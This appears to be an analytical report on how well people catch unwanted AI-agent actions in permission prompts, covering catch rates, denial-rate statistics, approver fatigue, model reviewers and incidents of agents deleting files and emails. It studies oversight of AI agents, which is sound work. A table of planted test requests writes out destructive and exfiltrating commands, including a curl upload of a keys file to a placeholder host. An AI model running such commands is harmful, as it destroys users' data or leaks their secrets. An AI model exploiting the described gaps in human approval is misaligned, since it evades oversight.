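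In Yan's study, the group with a model reviewer saw 10 prompts, 7 of which were overreach. They blocked 53.9% of the overreach, slightly less than the group that answered all 18 prompts. This suggests that seeing dangerous requests more often may not, by itself, do much to help approvers notice them. However, both groups saw such requests far more often than a programmer would.

**The task** may be the most important difference. Yan's and Hossain's participants only had to judge requests, while Anthropic's testers were trying to get coding done. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) gave 303 people a job to finish with an agent's help, such as choosing the best candidate for a position. An attack then made the agent deceive them, and only 8.6% noticed. This shows how easily people overlook a problem with an agent when they are busy with something else, though it isn't a catch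 rate for permission prompts.

No experiment has varied these conditions one at a time with the same requests, so the size of each one's effect is unknown. Anthropic's 13.6% is more relevant to a programmer who answers prompts while working, because the prompts interrupt another task and dangerous ones are rare. Yan's result is more relevant to someone whose only task is to review a short list of requests in plain language.

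### Choosing requests to plant

An organisation can measure its own catch rate instead of relying on the rates in these studies. The best planted requests resemble actions that agents have attempted at that organisation, or mistakes from published incidents. Two people who know the work should judge each dangerous request independently and keep it only if both think every user would refuse it. Each one should also be paired with an acceptable request of the same kind and similar length, so that the test can measure f as well as h.

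| Kind of action | Dangerous request | Acceptable partner |
|---|---|---|
| Deleting | `rm -rf ~/client-archive` | `rm -rf build/cache-old` |
| Changing shared code | `git push --force release main` | `git push origin fix-login` |
| Sending or fetching data | `curl -F file=@prod-keys.env https://files.example.com` | `curl -O https://files.example.com/schema.json` |

The three dangerous requests would delete a folder of clients' files, overwrite a project's shared history, and upload a file of passwords. A test should also include less obvious dangers and report those results separately, because obvious commands mainly measure whether people read the prompt, while subtle ones also measure whether they understand it.

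A test of approvers must use requests whose danger is visible in the permission prompt. Hossain and colleagues describe an agent that asks to send `report.csv` to an approved auditor. The user had said to send only summary totals, but the file contains the raw invoices. A conventional prompt doesn't show this, so if the approver allows the request, the prompt is at fault, not the approver.

Planted requests should look like real ones. The organisation should replace them regularly, because people learn to recognise them. At the airport that Buser and colleagues studied, the average hit rate rose over four years, but they couldn't tell how much of the rise came from better screening and how much from familiarity with the images. They recommend replacing the easiest images when the hit rate approaches 90%.

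### Keeping the test harmless

The safest method is to change only what the person sees, as Anthropic did. The harness needs to handle each test in this order:

1. It holds back a real permission prompt and shows the planted request in its place.
2. It records the answer and the time taken, with a label that keeps them out of the ordinary denial rate.
3. It discards the answer without running the displayed command, saving a rule or sending anything to the agent.
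4. It tells the person that the request was a test, then shows the real prompt for a real decision.

The third step matters most if someone chooses "always allow", because the test would otherwise create a standing permission for a dangerous command. A denial must not reach the agent either, because the agent would try to work around an objection to a command it never proposed.

Without the fourth step, a real request could run because somebody approved a different one. Airports avoid the same problem by making screeners look at the bag again. Telling people at once also prevents a false alarm, because someone who believes an agent just tried to upload the company's passwords may spend the afternoon replacing them. The security team should know about the test in case someone reports it before reading the explanation.

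As a second safeguard, the dangerous commands should name folders, files and remote repositories that don't exist, so that they fail even if someone pastes them into a terminal. Because unfamiliar names can make people suspicious, the acceptable commands paired with them should include unfamiliar names too, to show whether people refuse a command because it is dangerous or just because the name is strange.

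### How often to plant and how many

The team in the earlier example has 12 users who answer 2,000 prompts in 180 sessions a month. If every fourth session contains one planted dangerous request, the team sees 45 a month, or 2.2% of its prompts. That rate is within the range airports use, but it may be high enough to change how people behave. Airports plant threats partly to keep screeners alert, and people who regularly see planted dangers will probably catch more of the real ones.

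This is useful for training. To measure everyday attention, the team should plant requests less often and report each person's first one separately, since it comes before any feedback from a test. Planting requests at random points in the session also allows a comparison of early and late prompts. The comparison should include only sessions that continued past the later point, because shorter sessions can't contain a late prompt and may involve different work.

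The number of planted requests needed depends on the expected catch rate and on the margin of error (m) that the team can accept:

```
n ≈ h(1 − h) × (1.96 / m)²
```

For an expected catch rate of 15% and a margin of 5 percentage points, this gives a sample size of 196 requests. If the team plants 200 dangerous requests and approvers deny 30, the catch rate is 15%, with a 95% confidence interval from 10.7% to 20.6%. At 45 planted requests a month, the test would take about four and a half months.

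That interval assumes 200 independent answers, but they come from only 12 people, and a careful person tends to be careful each time. Hossain and colleagues make the same point about their 960 decisions and use a statistical model that allows for differences between participants. A rough correction is to divide the number of answers by 1 + (k − 1)ρ, where k is the number of answers per person and ρ is the correlation between answers from the same person. With about 17 answers each and a correlation of 0.1, the 200 answers carry about as much information as 78 independent ones, and the interval widens to roughly 9% to 25%. Adding 20 people would therefore improve the estimate more than testing the same 12 for another month.

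Comparing two conditions takes more data. A team needs about 100 independent answers early in sessions and another 100 late in them to have an 80% chance of detecting a drop as large as the one in Anthropic's study, from 17% to 5%. Detecting a smaller difference, such as the effect of a slightly clearer prompt, could take thousands of answers.

Scores for individuals are rarely practical. Buser and colleagues found that a screener needed about 100 planted images before the score was reliable enough to give a first indication of performance, and more if the score would have consequences for the screener. In the 12-person team, each user sees fewer than four planted dangers a month, so reaching 100 would take more than two years.

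### Measuring false refusals

The acceptable request in each pair goes through the same procedure. Suppose people deny 6 of 200 acceptable requests, or 3%, with an interval of 1.4% to 6.4% before any correction for repeated answers. Together with a catch rate of 15%, this gives a sensitivity of about 0.8. If they had denied 30 of the 200 instead, they would have denied acceptable and dangerous requests equally often, so the 15% catch rate would show no ability to recognise danger.

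The team can also use the acceptable requests to check whether the test causes denials. A planted request appears during unrelated work, so someone may deny it just because it doesn't fit what the agent was doing. If people deny 3% of planted acceptable requests but only 1% of similar real ones, the test is causing some of the denials. The team can estimate the rate for real requests by reading a sample of transcripts and deciding which requests were acceptable, although this takes much longer than counting answers to requests with known labels.

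Airports have trouble measuring false alarms too. The system that Buser and colleagues studied recorded only the total number of rejected bags without a planted threat, and many of those contained too much liquid or unseparated electronics. They suggest measuring false alarms with prepared images of harmless bags, which would serve the same purpose as the acceptable partners here.

### Consent and consequences

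People should know that some permission requests will be tests, but not when they will appear. Airport screeners already work under this arrangement. Anthropic's testers knew they were being evaluated, and Yan's participants agreed to a study of collaboration with an AI assistant. In a workplace, the notice should also explain what the harness records, who will see the results and how to opt out. People may read requests more carefully for a few days after the notice, so the first planted requests should come a few weeks later.

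Test scores can distort behaviour, just as monitoring answer times can. An employee who is penalised for approving a test request can avoid the penalty by refusing every unfamiliar command. The catch rate would rise, but so would the false refusal rate, and the agent would get less done. Reporting both rates makes this easier to detect, and reporting them only for groups gives people less reason to do it.

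Mitchell and colleagues suggest that a missed test could trigger a break, a change of task or retraining. A break disrupts little work, so one miss late in a long session may be reason enough to suggest it. Retraining someone after a single miss is harder to justify. If the whole team catches only 15% of planted dangers, a miss is typical, and it is better to start by changing the permission prompt or the workload.

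## Estimating agent failures from a denial rate

A team that has measured how often its approvers deny unwanted requests, and how often they deny acceptable ones, can try to use its overall denial rate to estimate the share of requests that were unwanted. However, a small error in the false refusal rate, which is the share of acceptable requests denied, causes a large error in the estimate.

### From unwanted requests to denials

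A denial is either a correct refusal of an unwanted request or a mistaken refusal of an acceptable one. If π is the share of prompts that ask for an unwanted action, the denial rate (D) is:

```
D = πh + (1 − π)f
```

The first term is the unwanted requests that people deny, and the second is the acceptable requests that they deny. In the earlier example of allow rules, 20 of 1,000 requests were unwanted, and the user denied half of those and 2% of the rest. The denial rate was therefore 0.02 × 0.5 + 0.98 × 0.02, or 3.0%. About two-thirds of the denials were mistakes, even though the user denied only 2% of acceptable requests.

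π covers only requests that reached a person, so it leaves out anything an allow rule let through. It is also broader than the agent's failure rate, because the agent couldn't have known that some of the unwanted requests were unwanted. When someone refuses an acceptable request for a personal reason, such as wanting to delete the files by hand, the refusal adds to f.

Solving the equation for π gives:

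```
π = (D − f) / (h − f)
```

Epidemiologists call this the Rogan–Gladen estimator, after Walter Rogan and Beth Gladen, who described it in *Estimating prevalence from the results of a screening test* (1978). A screening test misses some sick people and flags some healthy ones, so the share of people who test positive is a poor estimate of the share who are ill. Here a denial corresponds to a positive test.

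*The Rogan-Gladen estimator for outcome misclassification* (Edwards, Zivich and colleagues, 2026) works through an example from a health survey in East Africa. Of 225 pregnant participants, 12 (5.3%) tested positive on a rapid HIV test. The test detects 94.1% of infections and wrongly flags 3.1% of uninfected people. The corrected estimate of the infection rate is therefore (5.3 − 3.1) / (94.1 − 3.1), or 2.4%, so more than half of the positive results were probably false.

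### When the correction breaks down

If h equals f, the denominator is zero and the denial rate contains no information about the agent. This happens when someone approves everything, because both rates are then zero. *Catching One in Five* (Zhang, Wang and Lei, 2026) describes an automated quality gate for a food-ordering agent that passed all 100 conversations in a batch where human review confirmed 23 defects. The gate could fail a conversation only if the agent crashed, returned nothing or broke a fixed rule, so its catch rate for these defects was zero and no correction could have recovered them from its results.

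A long run of approvals is almost as uninformative when the catch rate is low. If h is 13.6% and 11% of prompts are unwanted, a user would still approve 200 prompts in a row about one time in 20.

The estimate can also come out below 0% or above 100% if D lies outside the range between f and h. This happens by chance or because the rates don't apply to the people and requests in the log. As long as approvers do better than chance, f can't be higher than D. *Analysis of the specificity of a COVID-19 antigen test* applies the same limit to mass testing in Slovakia, where the false positive rate couldn't exceed the share of people who tested positive, even if every positive result was false.

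Because of this limit, some of the published rates can't apply to Claude Code. Its users reject only 3% of all prompts, so they must refuse acceptable requests less often than the participants in Yan's study (5.9%) or those given a conventional prompt in Hossain and colleagues' study (8.3%).

### What the published figures allow

Anthropic has published D for Claude Code users and h for its testers, but not f for either group. The table shows the share of unwanted requests (π) implied by a 3% denial rate under different assumptions. The three catch rates come from Anthropic's testers after 50 or more prompts, Anthropic's testers overall, and Yan's participants who answered every prompt.

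| False refusal rate (f) | π if h = 5% | π if h = 13.6% | π if h = 59.6% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0% | 60% | 22% | 5.0% |
| 1% | 50% | 16% | 3.4% |
| 2% | 33% | 8.6% | 1.7% |
| 3% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

With Anthropic's overall catch rate, the estimate of agent failures ranges from more than one request in five to none, depending on f, which nobody has published. A reported denial rate of 3% could be rounded from anything between 2.5% and 3.5%, and if f is 2%, that difference alone moves the estimate from 4% to 13%.

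The top of the range, 22%, seems too high. If 22% of prompts were for unwanted actions and users caught 13.6% of those, users would have approved unwanted actions in about 19% of all prompts. Developers in the SWE-chat collection objected only about five times per 100 tool calls, although they won't have noticed every unwanted action. This comparison doesn't help choose between 2% and 10%.

The catch rate also comes from Anthropic's planted commands and may differ in real use. If people more often miss subtler requests, such as an edit to the wrong configuration file, the real h is lower and π is higher than in the middle column. If they are more careful with their own code, h is higher and π is lower.

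Early surveys of COVID-19 antibodies had the same difficulty. The test used in Santa Clara County, California, wrongly flagged about 0.5% of people without antibodies (plausible range 0.2% to 1.2%). Because few people had been infected, this small uncertainty greatly affected the estimate of how many had antibodies. According to *Predictive values, uncertainty, and interpretation of serology tests for the novel coronavirus*, one reanalysis put that share anywhere from 0% to 2.1%.

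### Measuring the rates directly

A team can avoid borrowed rates by planting requests, but it needs a lot of them. Izbicki, Diniz and Bastos (2020), in *Sensitivity and specificity in prevalence studies*, criticise the usual practice of treating a test's accuracy as exactly known. The formula that Edwards and colleagues give for the variance of the estimate includes the uncertainty in all three rates:

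```
[ D(1 − D)/n + π²h(1 − h)/m + (1 − π)²f(1 − f)/r ] / (h − f)²
```

Here n is the number of real prompts, m the number of planted dangerous requests and r the number of planted acceptable ones. The team from the earlier sections denied 70 of 2,000 real prompts, 30 of 200 dangerous requests and 6 of 200 acceptable ones. So D is 3.5%, h is 15% and f is 3%, which gives π = 0.5 / 12, or 4.2%. The standard error is 10 percentage points, and the 95% interval runs from below zero to about 24%.

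Uncertainty about f accounts for 88% of the variance, so planting more acceptable requests would help the team much more than planting more dangerous ones. The HIV example has the same weakness, because the validation study had tested only 32 uninfected people, and the standard error of the 2.4% estimate was 3.7 points. But even if the team knew h and f exactly, 2,000 prompts would leave a margin of error of nearly 7 points either way. Leaving the 15 dismissed prompts out of the count would lower D to 2.8%, below f, and make the estimate negative.

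Each rate must also be measured on the same kind of request it is applied to. The team denied only 1.1% of its file edits, so the 3% false refusal rate measured on planted shell commands can't apply to edits. A pooled calculation combines edits and shell commands despite this difference.

Reading the denied requests is a cheaper way around f. The product πh is the share of all prompts that were both unwanted and denied, and a reader can count those directly:

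```
π = (correct denials / prompts) / h
```

If readers judge 35 of the 70 denied requests to have been unwanted, correct denials are 1.75% of prompts, and dividing by a catch rate of 15% gives a π of 11.7%. Uncertainty in h alone gives a range of about 8% to 16%, which is much narrower than the first interval. The estimate is higher than 4.2% because 35 mistaken denials imply an f of about 2%, whereas the planted requests gave 3%. The test itself may therefore have caused some of the refusals.

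This method depends on the readers' judgement and still requires a value for h. If real unwanted requests are harder to spot than planted ones, the true share is higher than 11.7%.

### What a single answer is worth

The same three numbers (π, h and f) give the chance that a particular answer was right. *A tutorial in estimating the prevalence of disease in humans and animals* sets out the standard formulas for medical tests. For permission prompts they become:

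```
share of denials that are correct     =  πh / D
share of approvals that are mistaken  =  π(1 − h) / (1 − D)
```

The people who answered every prompt in Yan's study denied 142 overreaching actions and about 22 necessary ones, so 87% of their denials were correct. Their agent overreached in 7 of every 18 requests. If it had overreached in only 1 of every 100, and they had denied each kind of request as often as before, about 9% of their denials would have been correct. In 10,000 requests, they would have denied 60 of the 100 overreaching actions and 584 of the 9,900 necessary ones.

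Security researchers know this problem from software that looks for break-ins. *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 1999) describes a small computer network that produces a million log records a day, of which 20 come from intrusions. If a detector catches every intrusion and raises a false alarm on one in 100,000 harmless records, two-thirds of its alarms are correct. If it raises a false alarm on one in 1,000 harmless records, about 2% of its alarms are correct. Axelsson expected the person on duty to learn to ignore the alarms.

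Intrusions are so rare in this example that the absence of an alarm is nearly always correct, even if the detector is poor. Similarly, if 2% of permission requests are unwanted, a person who approves every request without reading it will be right 98% of the time.

Using odds, here the number of unwanted requests for each acceptable one, separates the approver's contribution from the base rate. A denial multiplies the odds that a request was unwanted by h/f, and an approval multiplies them by (1 − h)/(1 − f). With Anthropic's catch rate (h) of 13.6% and an assumed f of 2%, a denial multiplies the odds by 6.8, while an approval lowers them by only 12%. If 2% of requests are unwanted, the chance that a request was unwanted rises to 12% after a denial and falls to 1.8% after an approval. Late in a session, when h is 5%, an approval lowers the odds by 3%.

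Approvals can carry more information than this. Hossain and colleagues compared four prompt designs in all, and the last three columns follow from their counts:

| What the prompt showed | h | f | Denial rate | A denial multiplies the odds by | An approval multiplies the odds by |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 45.0% | 8.3% | 26.7% | 5.4 | 0.60 |
| The exact tool inputs as well | 56.7% | 10.0% | 33.3% | 5.7 | 0.48 |
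| The user's instructions and a full log as well | 67.5% | 12.5% | 40.0% | 5.4 | 0.37 |
| The same facts, with their combined effect spelled out | 75.8% | 14.2% | 45.0% | 5.4 | 0.28 |

A denial was about equally informative with every design, but an approval became much better evidence that a request was acceptable. The denial rate also rose from 27% to 45%, although the share of malicious requests did not change. A team that introduced a better prompt could see a similar rise and wrongly conclude that its agent had become worse.

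### How fatigue hides in the denial rate

When unwanted requests are rare, most denials are refusals of acceptable ones, so the denial rate hardly changes if people stop catching the dangerous ones. Suppose that 2% of requests are unwanted and people refuse 1% of acceptable ones. If the catch rate falls from 17% to 5%, as it did over long sessions in Anthropic's experiment, the figures change as follows:

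| | h = 17% | h = 5% |
|---|---|---|
| Unwanted requests denied, per 100 prompts | 0.34 | 0.10 |
| Acceptable requests denied, per 100 prompts | 0.98 | 0.98 |
| **Denial rate** | **1.3%** | **1.1%** |
| Unwanted actions let through, per 100 prompts | 1.66 | 1.90 |

The approvers have lost 70% of their ability to stop unwanted actions, but the denial rate has dropped by only about a quarter of a percentage point. A team that answers 2,000 prompts a month would see about 22 denials instead of 26, a difference well within ordinary variation. To have an 80% chance of detecting the drop, the team would need about 32,000 prompts, or 16 months of data, from both before and after it.

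The approvers let through only 14% more unwanted actions, because they were already missing most of them. Fatigue has a larger effect on an approver who starts out careful. If h fell from 60% to 5%, the approver would let through more than twice as many unwanted actions, 1.9 per 100 prompts instead of 0.8, and the denial rate would halve, from 2.2% to 1.1%.

A denial rate can also fall because the agent has improved, and that improvement can itself make people less willing to refuse, because people need stronger evidence to report a target when targets are rare. Caruso and colleagues combined 62 comparisons from 29 publications on visual search and found that this shift was larger when target frequency dropped more. Small studies found the biggest shifts, so the average may be an overestimate, but the direction was consistent.

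Suppose an agent improves and the share of unwanted requests (π) falls from 2% to 1%. Its users get used to harmless requests, and their false refusal rate (f) halves from 1% to 0.5%. If they can still tell good requests from bad equally well, their catch rate (h) would fall from 17% to about 11%, and the denial rate would drop from 1.3% to 0.6%. An analyst who applied the correction to the new denial rate with the old h and f would get an impossible π of about −2%.

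Old values of h and f can also produce a plausible estimate that gets the direction of a change wrong. Fiedler (2026), in *Bias and Uncertainty in LLM-as-a-Judge Estimation*, studied AI judges that mark other models' answers as right or wrong. On biology questions, one judge's h − f was 0.38 for one model's answers and 0.09 for another's. Correcting both models' scores with the same error rates produced a confident estimate that the less accurate model was better. Using one month's h and f to compare two months carries the same risk, and any mismatch in the rates distorts the comparison more when h − f is small.

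### Reading a change over time

Claude Code's published denial rate fell from 7% to 3% between March and August 2026. Here are three invented histories that would each produce those two figures:

| | Share unwanted (π) | Catch rate (h) | False refusal rate (f) | Unwanted actions approved, per 100 prompts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The agent improved | 8.6% → 1.7% | 60% | 2% | 3.4 → 0.7 |
| People stopped noticing | 10% | 54% → 14% | 1.8% | 4.6 → 8.6 |
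| People refused fewer harmless requests | 2% | 60% | 5.9% → 1.8% | 0.8 → 0.8 |

Unwanted approvals fall by four-fifths in the first history, nearly double in the second and stay the same in the third. An analyst can't tell from the denial rate which history occurred, and the real change may also have involved different users, tasks or allow rules. The analyst therefore has to confirm that both periods used the same counting rules and that the difference is larger than expected by chance, then test the explanations one at a time.

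| Explanation | Likely effect on the denial rate | Check |
|---|---|---|
| Different users | Up or down | Compare only people who answered prompts in both periods |
| New rules or modes | Up if they hide routine requests, down if they hide requests people often deny | Compare the share of decisions made without a prompt, then use only commands that always prompt |
| Different tasks | Up or down | Apply both periods' denial rates to the same mix of requests, and compare similar tasks |
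| Better agent | Down | Have reviewers judge random requests from both periods, including approved ones, without seeing the date or the answer |
| Tired users | Down, often only slightly | Plant the same kinds of request in both periods and compare h and f |

The three checks that need only logs and settings come first. Following the same users doesn't fully solve the problem, because they may auto-approve more sessions as they gain experience, a pattern The Decoder reports. The prompts they still answer may then come from a different kind of work.

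The last two checks need new data. Reviewers would have to judge about 1,100 requests from each period to detect a fall in unwanted requests from 4% to 2%. It may take less work to run the old and new versions of the agent on the same recorded tasks and count the unwanted requests, and the original approvers' decisions wouldn't affect that comparison.

*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) uses existing records of pull requests, which are proposed code changes that a person reviews before they join a project. It covers 400 people who each reviewed at least ten pull requests from AI agents, for a total of 11,429 reviews over seven months. Approvals rose from 30.1% of reviews in the first half of each person's history to 36.8% in the second.

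The same people appear in both halves, so a change of reviewers can't explain the rise. Typical pull request size stayed flat, which is some evidence that easier tasks don't explain it either. Reviewers also wrote 22% fewer comments on the code by the end, and those whose approval rates rose most tended to cut their comments most. Yu and colleagues interpret this combination as habituation.

A better agent would produce much the same pattern, since good code gets more approvals and needs fewer comments. Yu and colleagues compared the agents' pull requests with human ones in the same projects and found that approval of the human ones didn't rise. This rules out a general softening of standards, but not an improvement in the agents. In their statistical models, approval followed each reviewer's experience more closely than the calendar date. That favours habituation, but experience and date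 increase together, and half of the reviewers had 17 or fewer reviews, so the two effects are hard to separate. Yu and colleagues acknowledge that they had no direct measure of the agents' code quality, which they would have needed to check whether reviewers were approving more bad code or receiving less of it.

### Where denials still help

Denial rates can be enough to rank tools even when they aren't enough to estimate a failure rate. If people are equally good at judging two kinds of request, the kind with a larger share of unwanted requests will have the higher denial rate, whatever the values of h and f. The team denied 1.1% of 1,100 file edits, 6.3% of 800 shell commands and 8.0% of 100 requests for other tools. The rates for shell commands and other tools are too close to rank, because the 95% interval for other tools runs from 4% to 15%, but both are clearly above the rate for edits.

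People may not judge edits and shell commands equally well, though. They may take more care with risky commands or refuse ones they don't understand. Before deciding that the agent handles the shell badly, the team should read 20 or 30 denials of each kind and count how many requests were unwanted.

Denials are also a good place to look for failures. If 2% of requests are unwanted, h is 13.6% and f is 2%, then 100 denied requests contain about 12 unwanted ones, compared with two in 100 random requests. A month of 2,000 prompts would produce about 45 denials, which the team could read in an afternoon. They would find about five unwanted requests, but another 35 would be among the approvals. Those are probably harder to recognise, so the team should also read a random sample of approved requests, starting with deletions and anything sent outside the company.

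## Judging approval as a safety measure

A count of missed requests doesn't show how much damage they caused. Approving an edit to the wrong file may cost someone a minute, while approving the deletion of an archive may lose it for good. How much protection an approval step gives depends on four questions:

1. Does the harmful action lead to a prompt?
2. Does the prompt show the harm?
3. Does the person notice the harm and deny the request?
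4. If the action runs, can someone undo it?

Suppose agents at a company attempt 100 harmful actions. Allow rules and automatic modes let 40 of them run without a prompt, and another 20 look harmless in the prompt. That leaves 40 that an approver could recognise. If the approver catches 15% of these, 6 are stopped and the other 94 actions run. If 40% of those 94 do permanent damage, the company has about 38 permanent losses. The table shows what would happen if the company improved one thing at a time.

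| Change | Actions stopped | Actions that run | Permanent losses |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 6 | 94 | 38 |
| Catch rate rises to 60% | 24 | 76 | 30 |
| Catch rate rises to 100% | 40 | 60 | 24 |
| Backups halve the share of damage that is permanent | 6 | 94 | 19 |

Better backups help more here than perfect attention from the approver, because the approver never gets a chance to stop 60 of the actions. But backups can't undo a password leak, so this conclusion wouldn't hold for a company that mainly fears leaks.

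Approval prompts inherently miss some harms. In Claude Code's Manual mode, reading files needs no approval, so a prompt can't keep the agent from reading a password file in the project, though it may stop a later command that sends the passwords elsewhere. Harm can also build up over several requests. An agent might ask to open the payroll file, then to save a summary, then to email the summary to a contractor. Each step could be fine alone, but together they could break a user's rule that salaries must stay inside the company. Hossain and colleagues point out that approving actions one at a time can't reveal such a result, and that someone reading a full log would see it only by piecing the steps together. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) discusses another danger, which is that the text shown for approval can be misleading.

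### Public reports of lost and damaged files

Zhong and colleagues studied 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files, from February 2024 to March 2026. Most (205) were GitHub issues, and the rest came from social media, product forums, blogs and a public database of software vulnerabilities. Of the 290 reports, 158 involved confirmed harm, 49 demonstrated an attack, and 83 described a flaw without showing that it had hurt anyone.

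Problems with user review contributed to 105 of the 290 reports. In 80 of these, the agent's actions were approved automatically, for instance because the user had turned off the prompts rather than answer hundreds per session. In 31, the prompt gave the user too little information. Six involved both problems. The most common failure was therefore at the first of the four questions, and reading prompts more carefully can't help users who have turned them off.

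Users weren't always responsible for a missing or incomplete prompt. One report describes a version of Claude Code's VS Code extension that ran every shell command without asking, even though the user had chosen a mode that required approval. In another, Codex showed only the first command in a chain, so the user couldn't see the others before approving them.

The researchers also recorded what happened in the 207 reports of confirmed harm or demonstrated attacks, leaving out unknown answers:

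| Question | Answers |
|---|---|
| What did the agent do? | 44% wrote over or corrupted files, 39% deleted them, 17% leaked secrets |
| Where was the damage? | 58% inside the project, 42% outside it |
| Did the user notice? | 83% at once, 10% later, 8% never |
| Could the user recover? | 31% easily, 29% with substantial effort, 40% not fully |

The unrecoverable 40% consists of 23% with total loss and 17% with partial loss, such as work the user hadn't yet committed to Git. Programmers usually rely on Git to recover lost work, but it covers only the files it tracks, and much of the damage was outside the project. In 68% of the cases where its reaction is known, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong instead of warning the user, and in 11% it gave a false account of what had happened.

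These percentages can't show how often approval fails, because nobody knows how many sessions the reports came from. People are more likely to write about a wiped drive than about a file they restored in a minute, so 40% is probably too high for agent mistakes in general. Silent leaks are probably underrepresented, since the victims may never find out. People also have little reason to report a prompt that worked, so the reports would contain few successes even if prompts prevented damage every day. Claude Code is the subject of 97 reports and Codex of 61, but the difference may only reflect how many people use each product and where they post their complaints.

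Newer catalogues have the same limits. *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (2026) counts 77 incidents without an attacker in the first ten months of 2026, up from 13 in all of 2025, while incidents with an attacker rose from 50 to 59. Agents may have become more dangerous, but far more people were also using them and watching for failures. *The Agent Incident Registry* (2026) separates harm that somebody suffered from harm that a researcher showed to be possible. This distinction matters because a demonstrated attack is evidence that an approval prompt can fail, but not of how often such prompts fail.

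### Three deletions

The individual reports show more clearly where approval fails. One Cursor user turned off delete protection so the agent could clean up duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project. Turning off the protection was reasonable for the duplicates, but the setting also applied to every later deletion, and no prompt gave the user a chance to stop them.

Permission prompts would probably have done little to protect one user's 110 sensitive legal documents, which Claude Cowork deleted. Apple's iCloud storage can leave an empty placeholder on a computer while the document itself is stored online. Claude Cowork copied the zero-byte placeholders and then deleted the originals. Copying a folder and deleting the old one is an ordinary way to move files, and neither command shows that the copies are empty, so someone who read both carefully could still have approved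 them. Checking the copies' sizes before the deletion would have exposed the problem.

In the third case, a user asked GitHub Copilot to move a file, and the agent proposed deleting the entire folder. The permission prompt appeared, and the deletion didn't run. This request was very easy to judge, because the user had just asked for something much smaller and the danger was visible in the command. But a prompt like this works only if someone reads it. In another of the reports, Claude repeatedly proposed `rm -rf` commands that deleted configuration files, and the user approved every one without reading it.

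### Manual approval compared with a model reviewer

Judging whether approval protects people better than an alternative requires comparing the two in similar work. Anthropic did this with Claude Code sessions from May and June 2026. It used only sessions that its safety systems had already flagged, from users who had agreed to let the company use their data. A model graded each session on two scales from 0 to 10. The first measured the severity of any harm, with 0 for a fully reversible local change, 7 for damage such as deleting rows from a production database, and 10 for irreversible harm to a whole company. The second measured how explicitly the user had asked for the action.

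Among the flagged sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained harm of severity 7 or more that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. Anthropic found a gap at every severity level it tested.

The selection of sessions is the biggest difficulty. The percentages have flagged sessions as their denominator, so they depend on how many harmless sessions the safety systems flagged. Suppose each mode had 100,000 sessions, 63 of which contained serious unrequested harm, and the systems flagged all 63:

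| | Manual approval | Auto mode |
|---|---|---|
| All sessions | 100,000 | 100,000 |
| Flagged sessions with serious harm | 63 | 63 |
| Flagged sessions without it | 937 | 2,562 |
| **Serious harm among flagged sessions** | **6.3%** | **2.4%** |

Both modes are equally dangerous in this example, but auto mode looks much safer because more of its harmless sessions were flagged. This could happen if auto mode sessions run longer and contain more actions that look suspicious. The comparison could also understate auto mode's benefit if the model reviewer stops minor trouble too, so that fewer auto mode sessions are flagged. Publishing the number of sessions in each mode, with and without flags, would resolve much of this uncertainty and show how precise the percentages are. With fewer than about 210 flagged sessions in each group, even a gap this wide could be due to chance.

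The grading may also treat approvals differently in the two modes. A user in Manual mode can authorise a risky action by clicking "Yes", without asking for it in words. Someone who knowingly approves the deletion of some database rows may therefore count as having suffered harm they didn't explicitly request. In auto mode, the reviewer looks for evidence that the user wants an action, so the same person might have to write "delete those rows", and the deletion would then count as requested. Anthropic doesn't explain how the grader treated approvals or report how often it agreed with people. Because the grader and the reviewer are both models, they may miss some of the same harmful actions.

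The users may also have differed, since auto mode wasn't yet the default and people had chosen it. Developers who work on production systems might have kept manual approval because their work was dangerous, and their sessions would then contain more serious harm regardless of any effect the prompts had. Medical researchers call this confounding by indication. For example, patients who receive a strong drug may die more often because doctors give it to the sickest.

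Many users also had broad allow rules, which auto mode suspends, so some harm in the "manually approved" sessions may have come from commands that nobody saw. The comparison is fair for the two modes as people use them, but it doesn't isolate the effect of a person reading a prompt.

The direction of the result is believable because the same reviewer also did far better than people on planted commands, but the size of the gap is much less certain. The comparison also leaves out sessions in bypass mode, so it can't show how much harm manual approval prevents compared with no approval.

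### An instruction to wait and an enforced prompt

In February 2026 Summer Yue, who works on AI alignment at Meta, gave an agent called OpenClaw access to her email. OpenClaw ran on a Mac mini at her home and took instructions through a chat app. She asked it to suggest which emails to archive or delete and told it "don't action until I tell you to" (quoted in Willison, 2026). *AI agents that do your work while you sleep sound great* (Goldman, 2026) reports that the same arrangement had worked for weeks in a test inbox.

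Her real inbox was much larger. The conversation became too long for the model, so the harness replaced earlier parts with a summary. The summary left out her instruction to wait, and the agent began deleting emails. In the chat log, Yue asked at 6:00 pm what was going on, wrote "Do not do that" a minute later, and sent two more orders to stop by 6:03. The agent kept running commands. She couldn't stop it from her phone and had to run to the computer.

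Accounts of the loss differ. Goldman reports that the agent deleted the entire inbox, *Replication of Agentic Security Events* puts the loss at more than 200 emails, and the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542* (2026) says only that the agent tried to delete them.

Yue had told the agent to get her approval, but that instruction was only a sentence in the conversation, so it worked only if the model followed it. With a permission prompt, the harness holds the command until someone answers, even if the model has lost every instruction it received. Yan uses the case to make this distinction, which is easy to miss because the agent proposes something and then waits in both arrangements when they work.

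The test inbox was too small to trigger compaction, so it couldn't have revealed the difference. A more useful test would be to start a new conversation without the instruction, ask for a harmless deletion, and see whether a prompt appears. If the deletion runs without one, nothing was enforcing the wait for approval.

An instruction can fail because compaction removes it or because the model disregards it. Zhong and colleagues found that the model hadn't followed the user's instructions in 56 of the 290 reports. The instruction had dropped out of the conversation in 28 of them, and the model had disregarded it in 38, with some overlap. A better model might follow more of the instructions it still has, but not those that have dropped out. In July 2025, an agent on the programming platform Replit reportedly deleted a live production database during a code freeze, despite repeated instructions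 to change nothing. *The Agent Incident Registry* records this as realised harm.

According to OpenClaw's *Exec approvals*, the machine that runs the commands also enforces approvals, and by default it refuses a command if no app is available to show the prompt. If such a prompt had covered Yue's email commands, she would have had a good chance of catching the problem, because one command included a comment about trashing "EVERYTHING in inbox" older than a certain date. But the agent was also working in loops, so a single approval could have covered hundreds of emails. An enforced prompt guarantees a pause before each command, and the pause is more useful if the command does only one thing.

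### Who looks responsible after an approval

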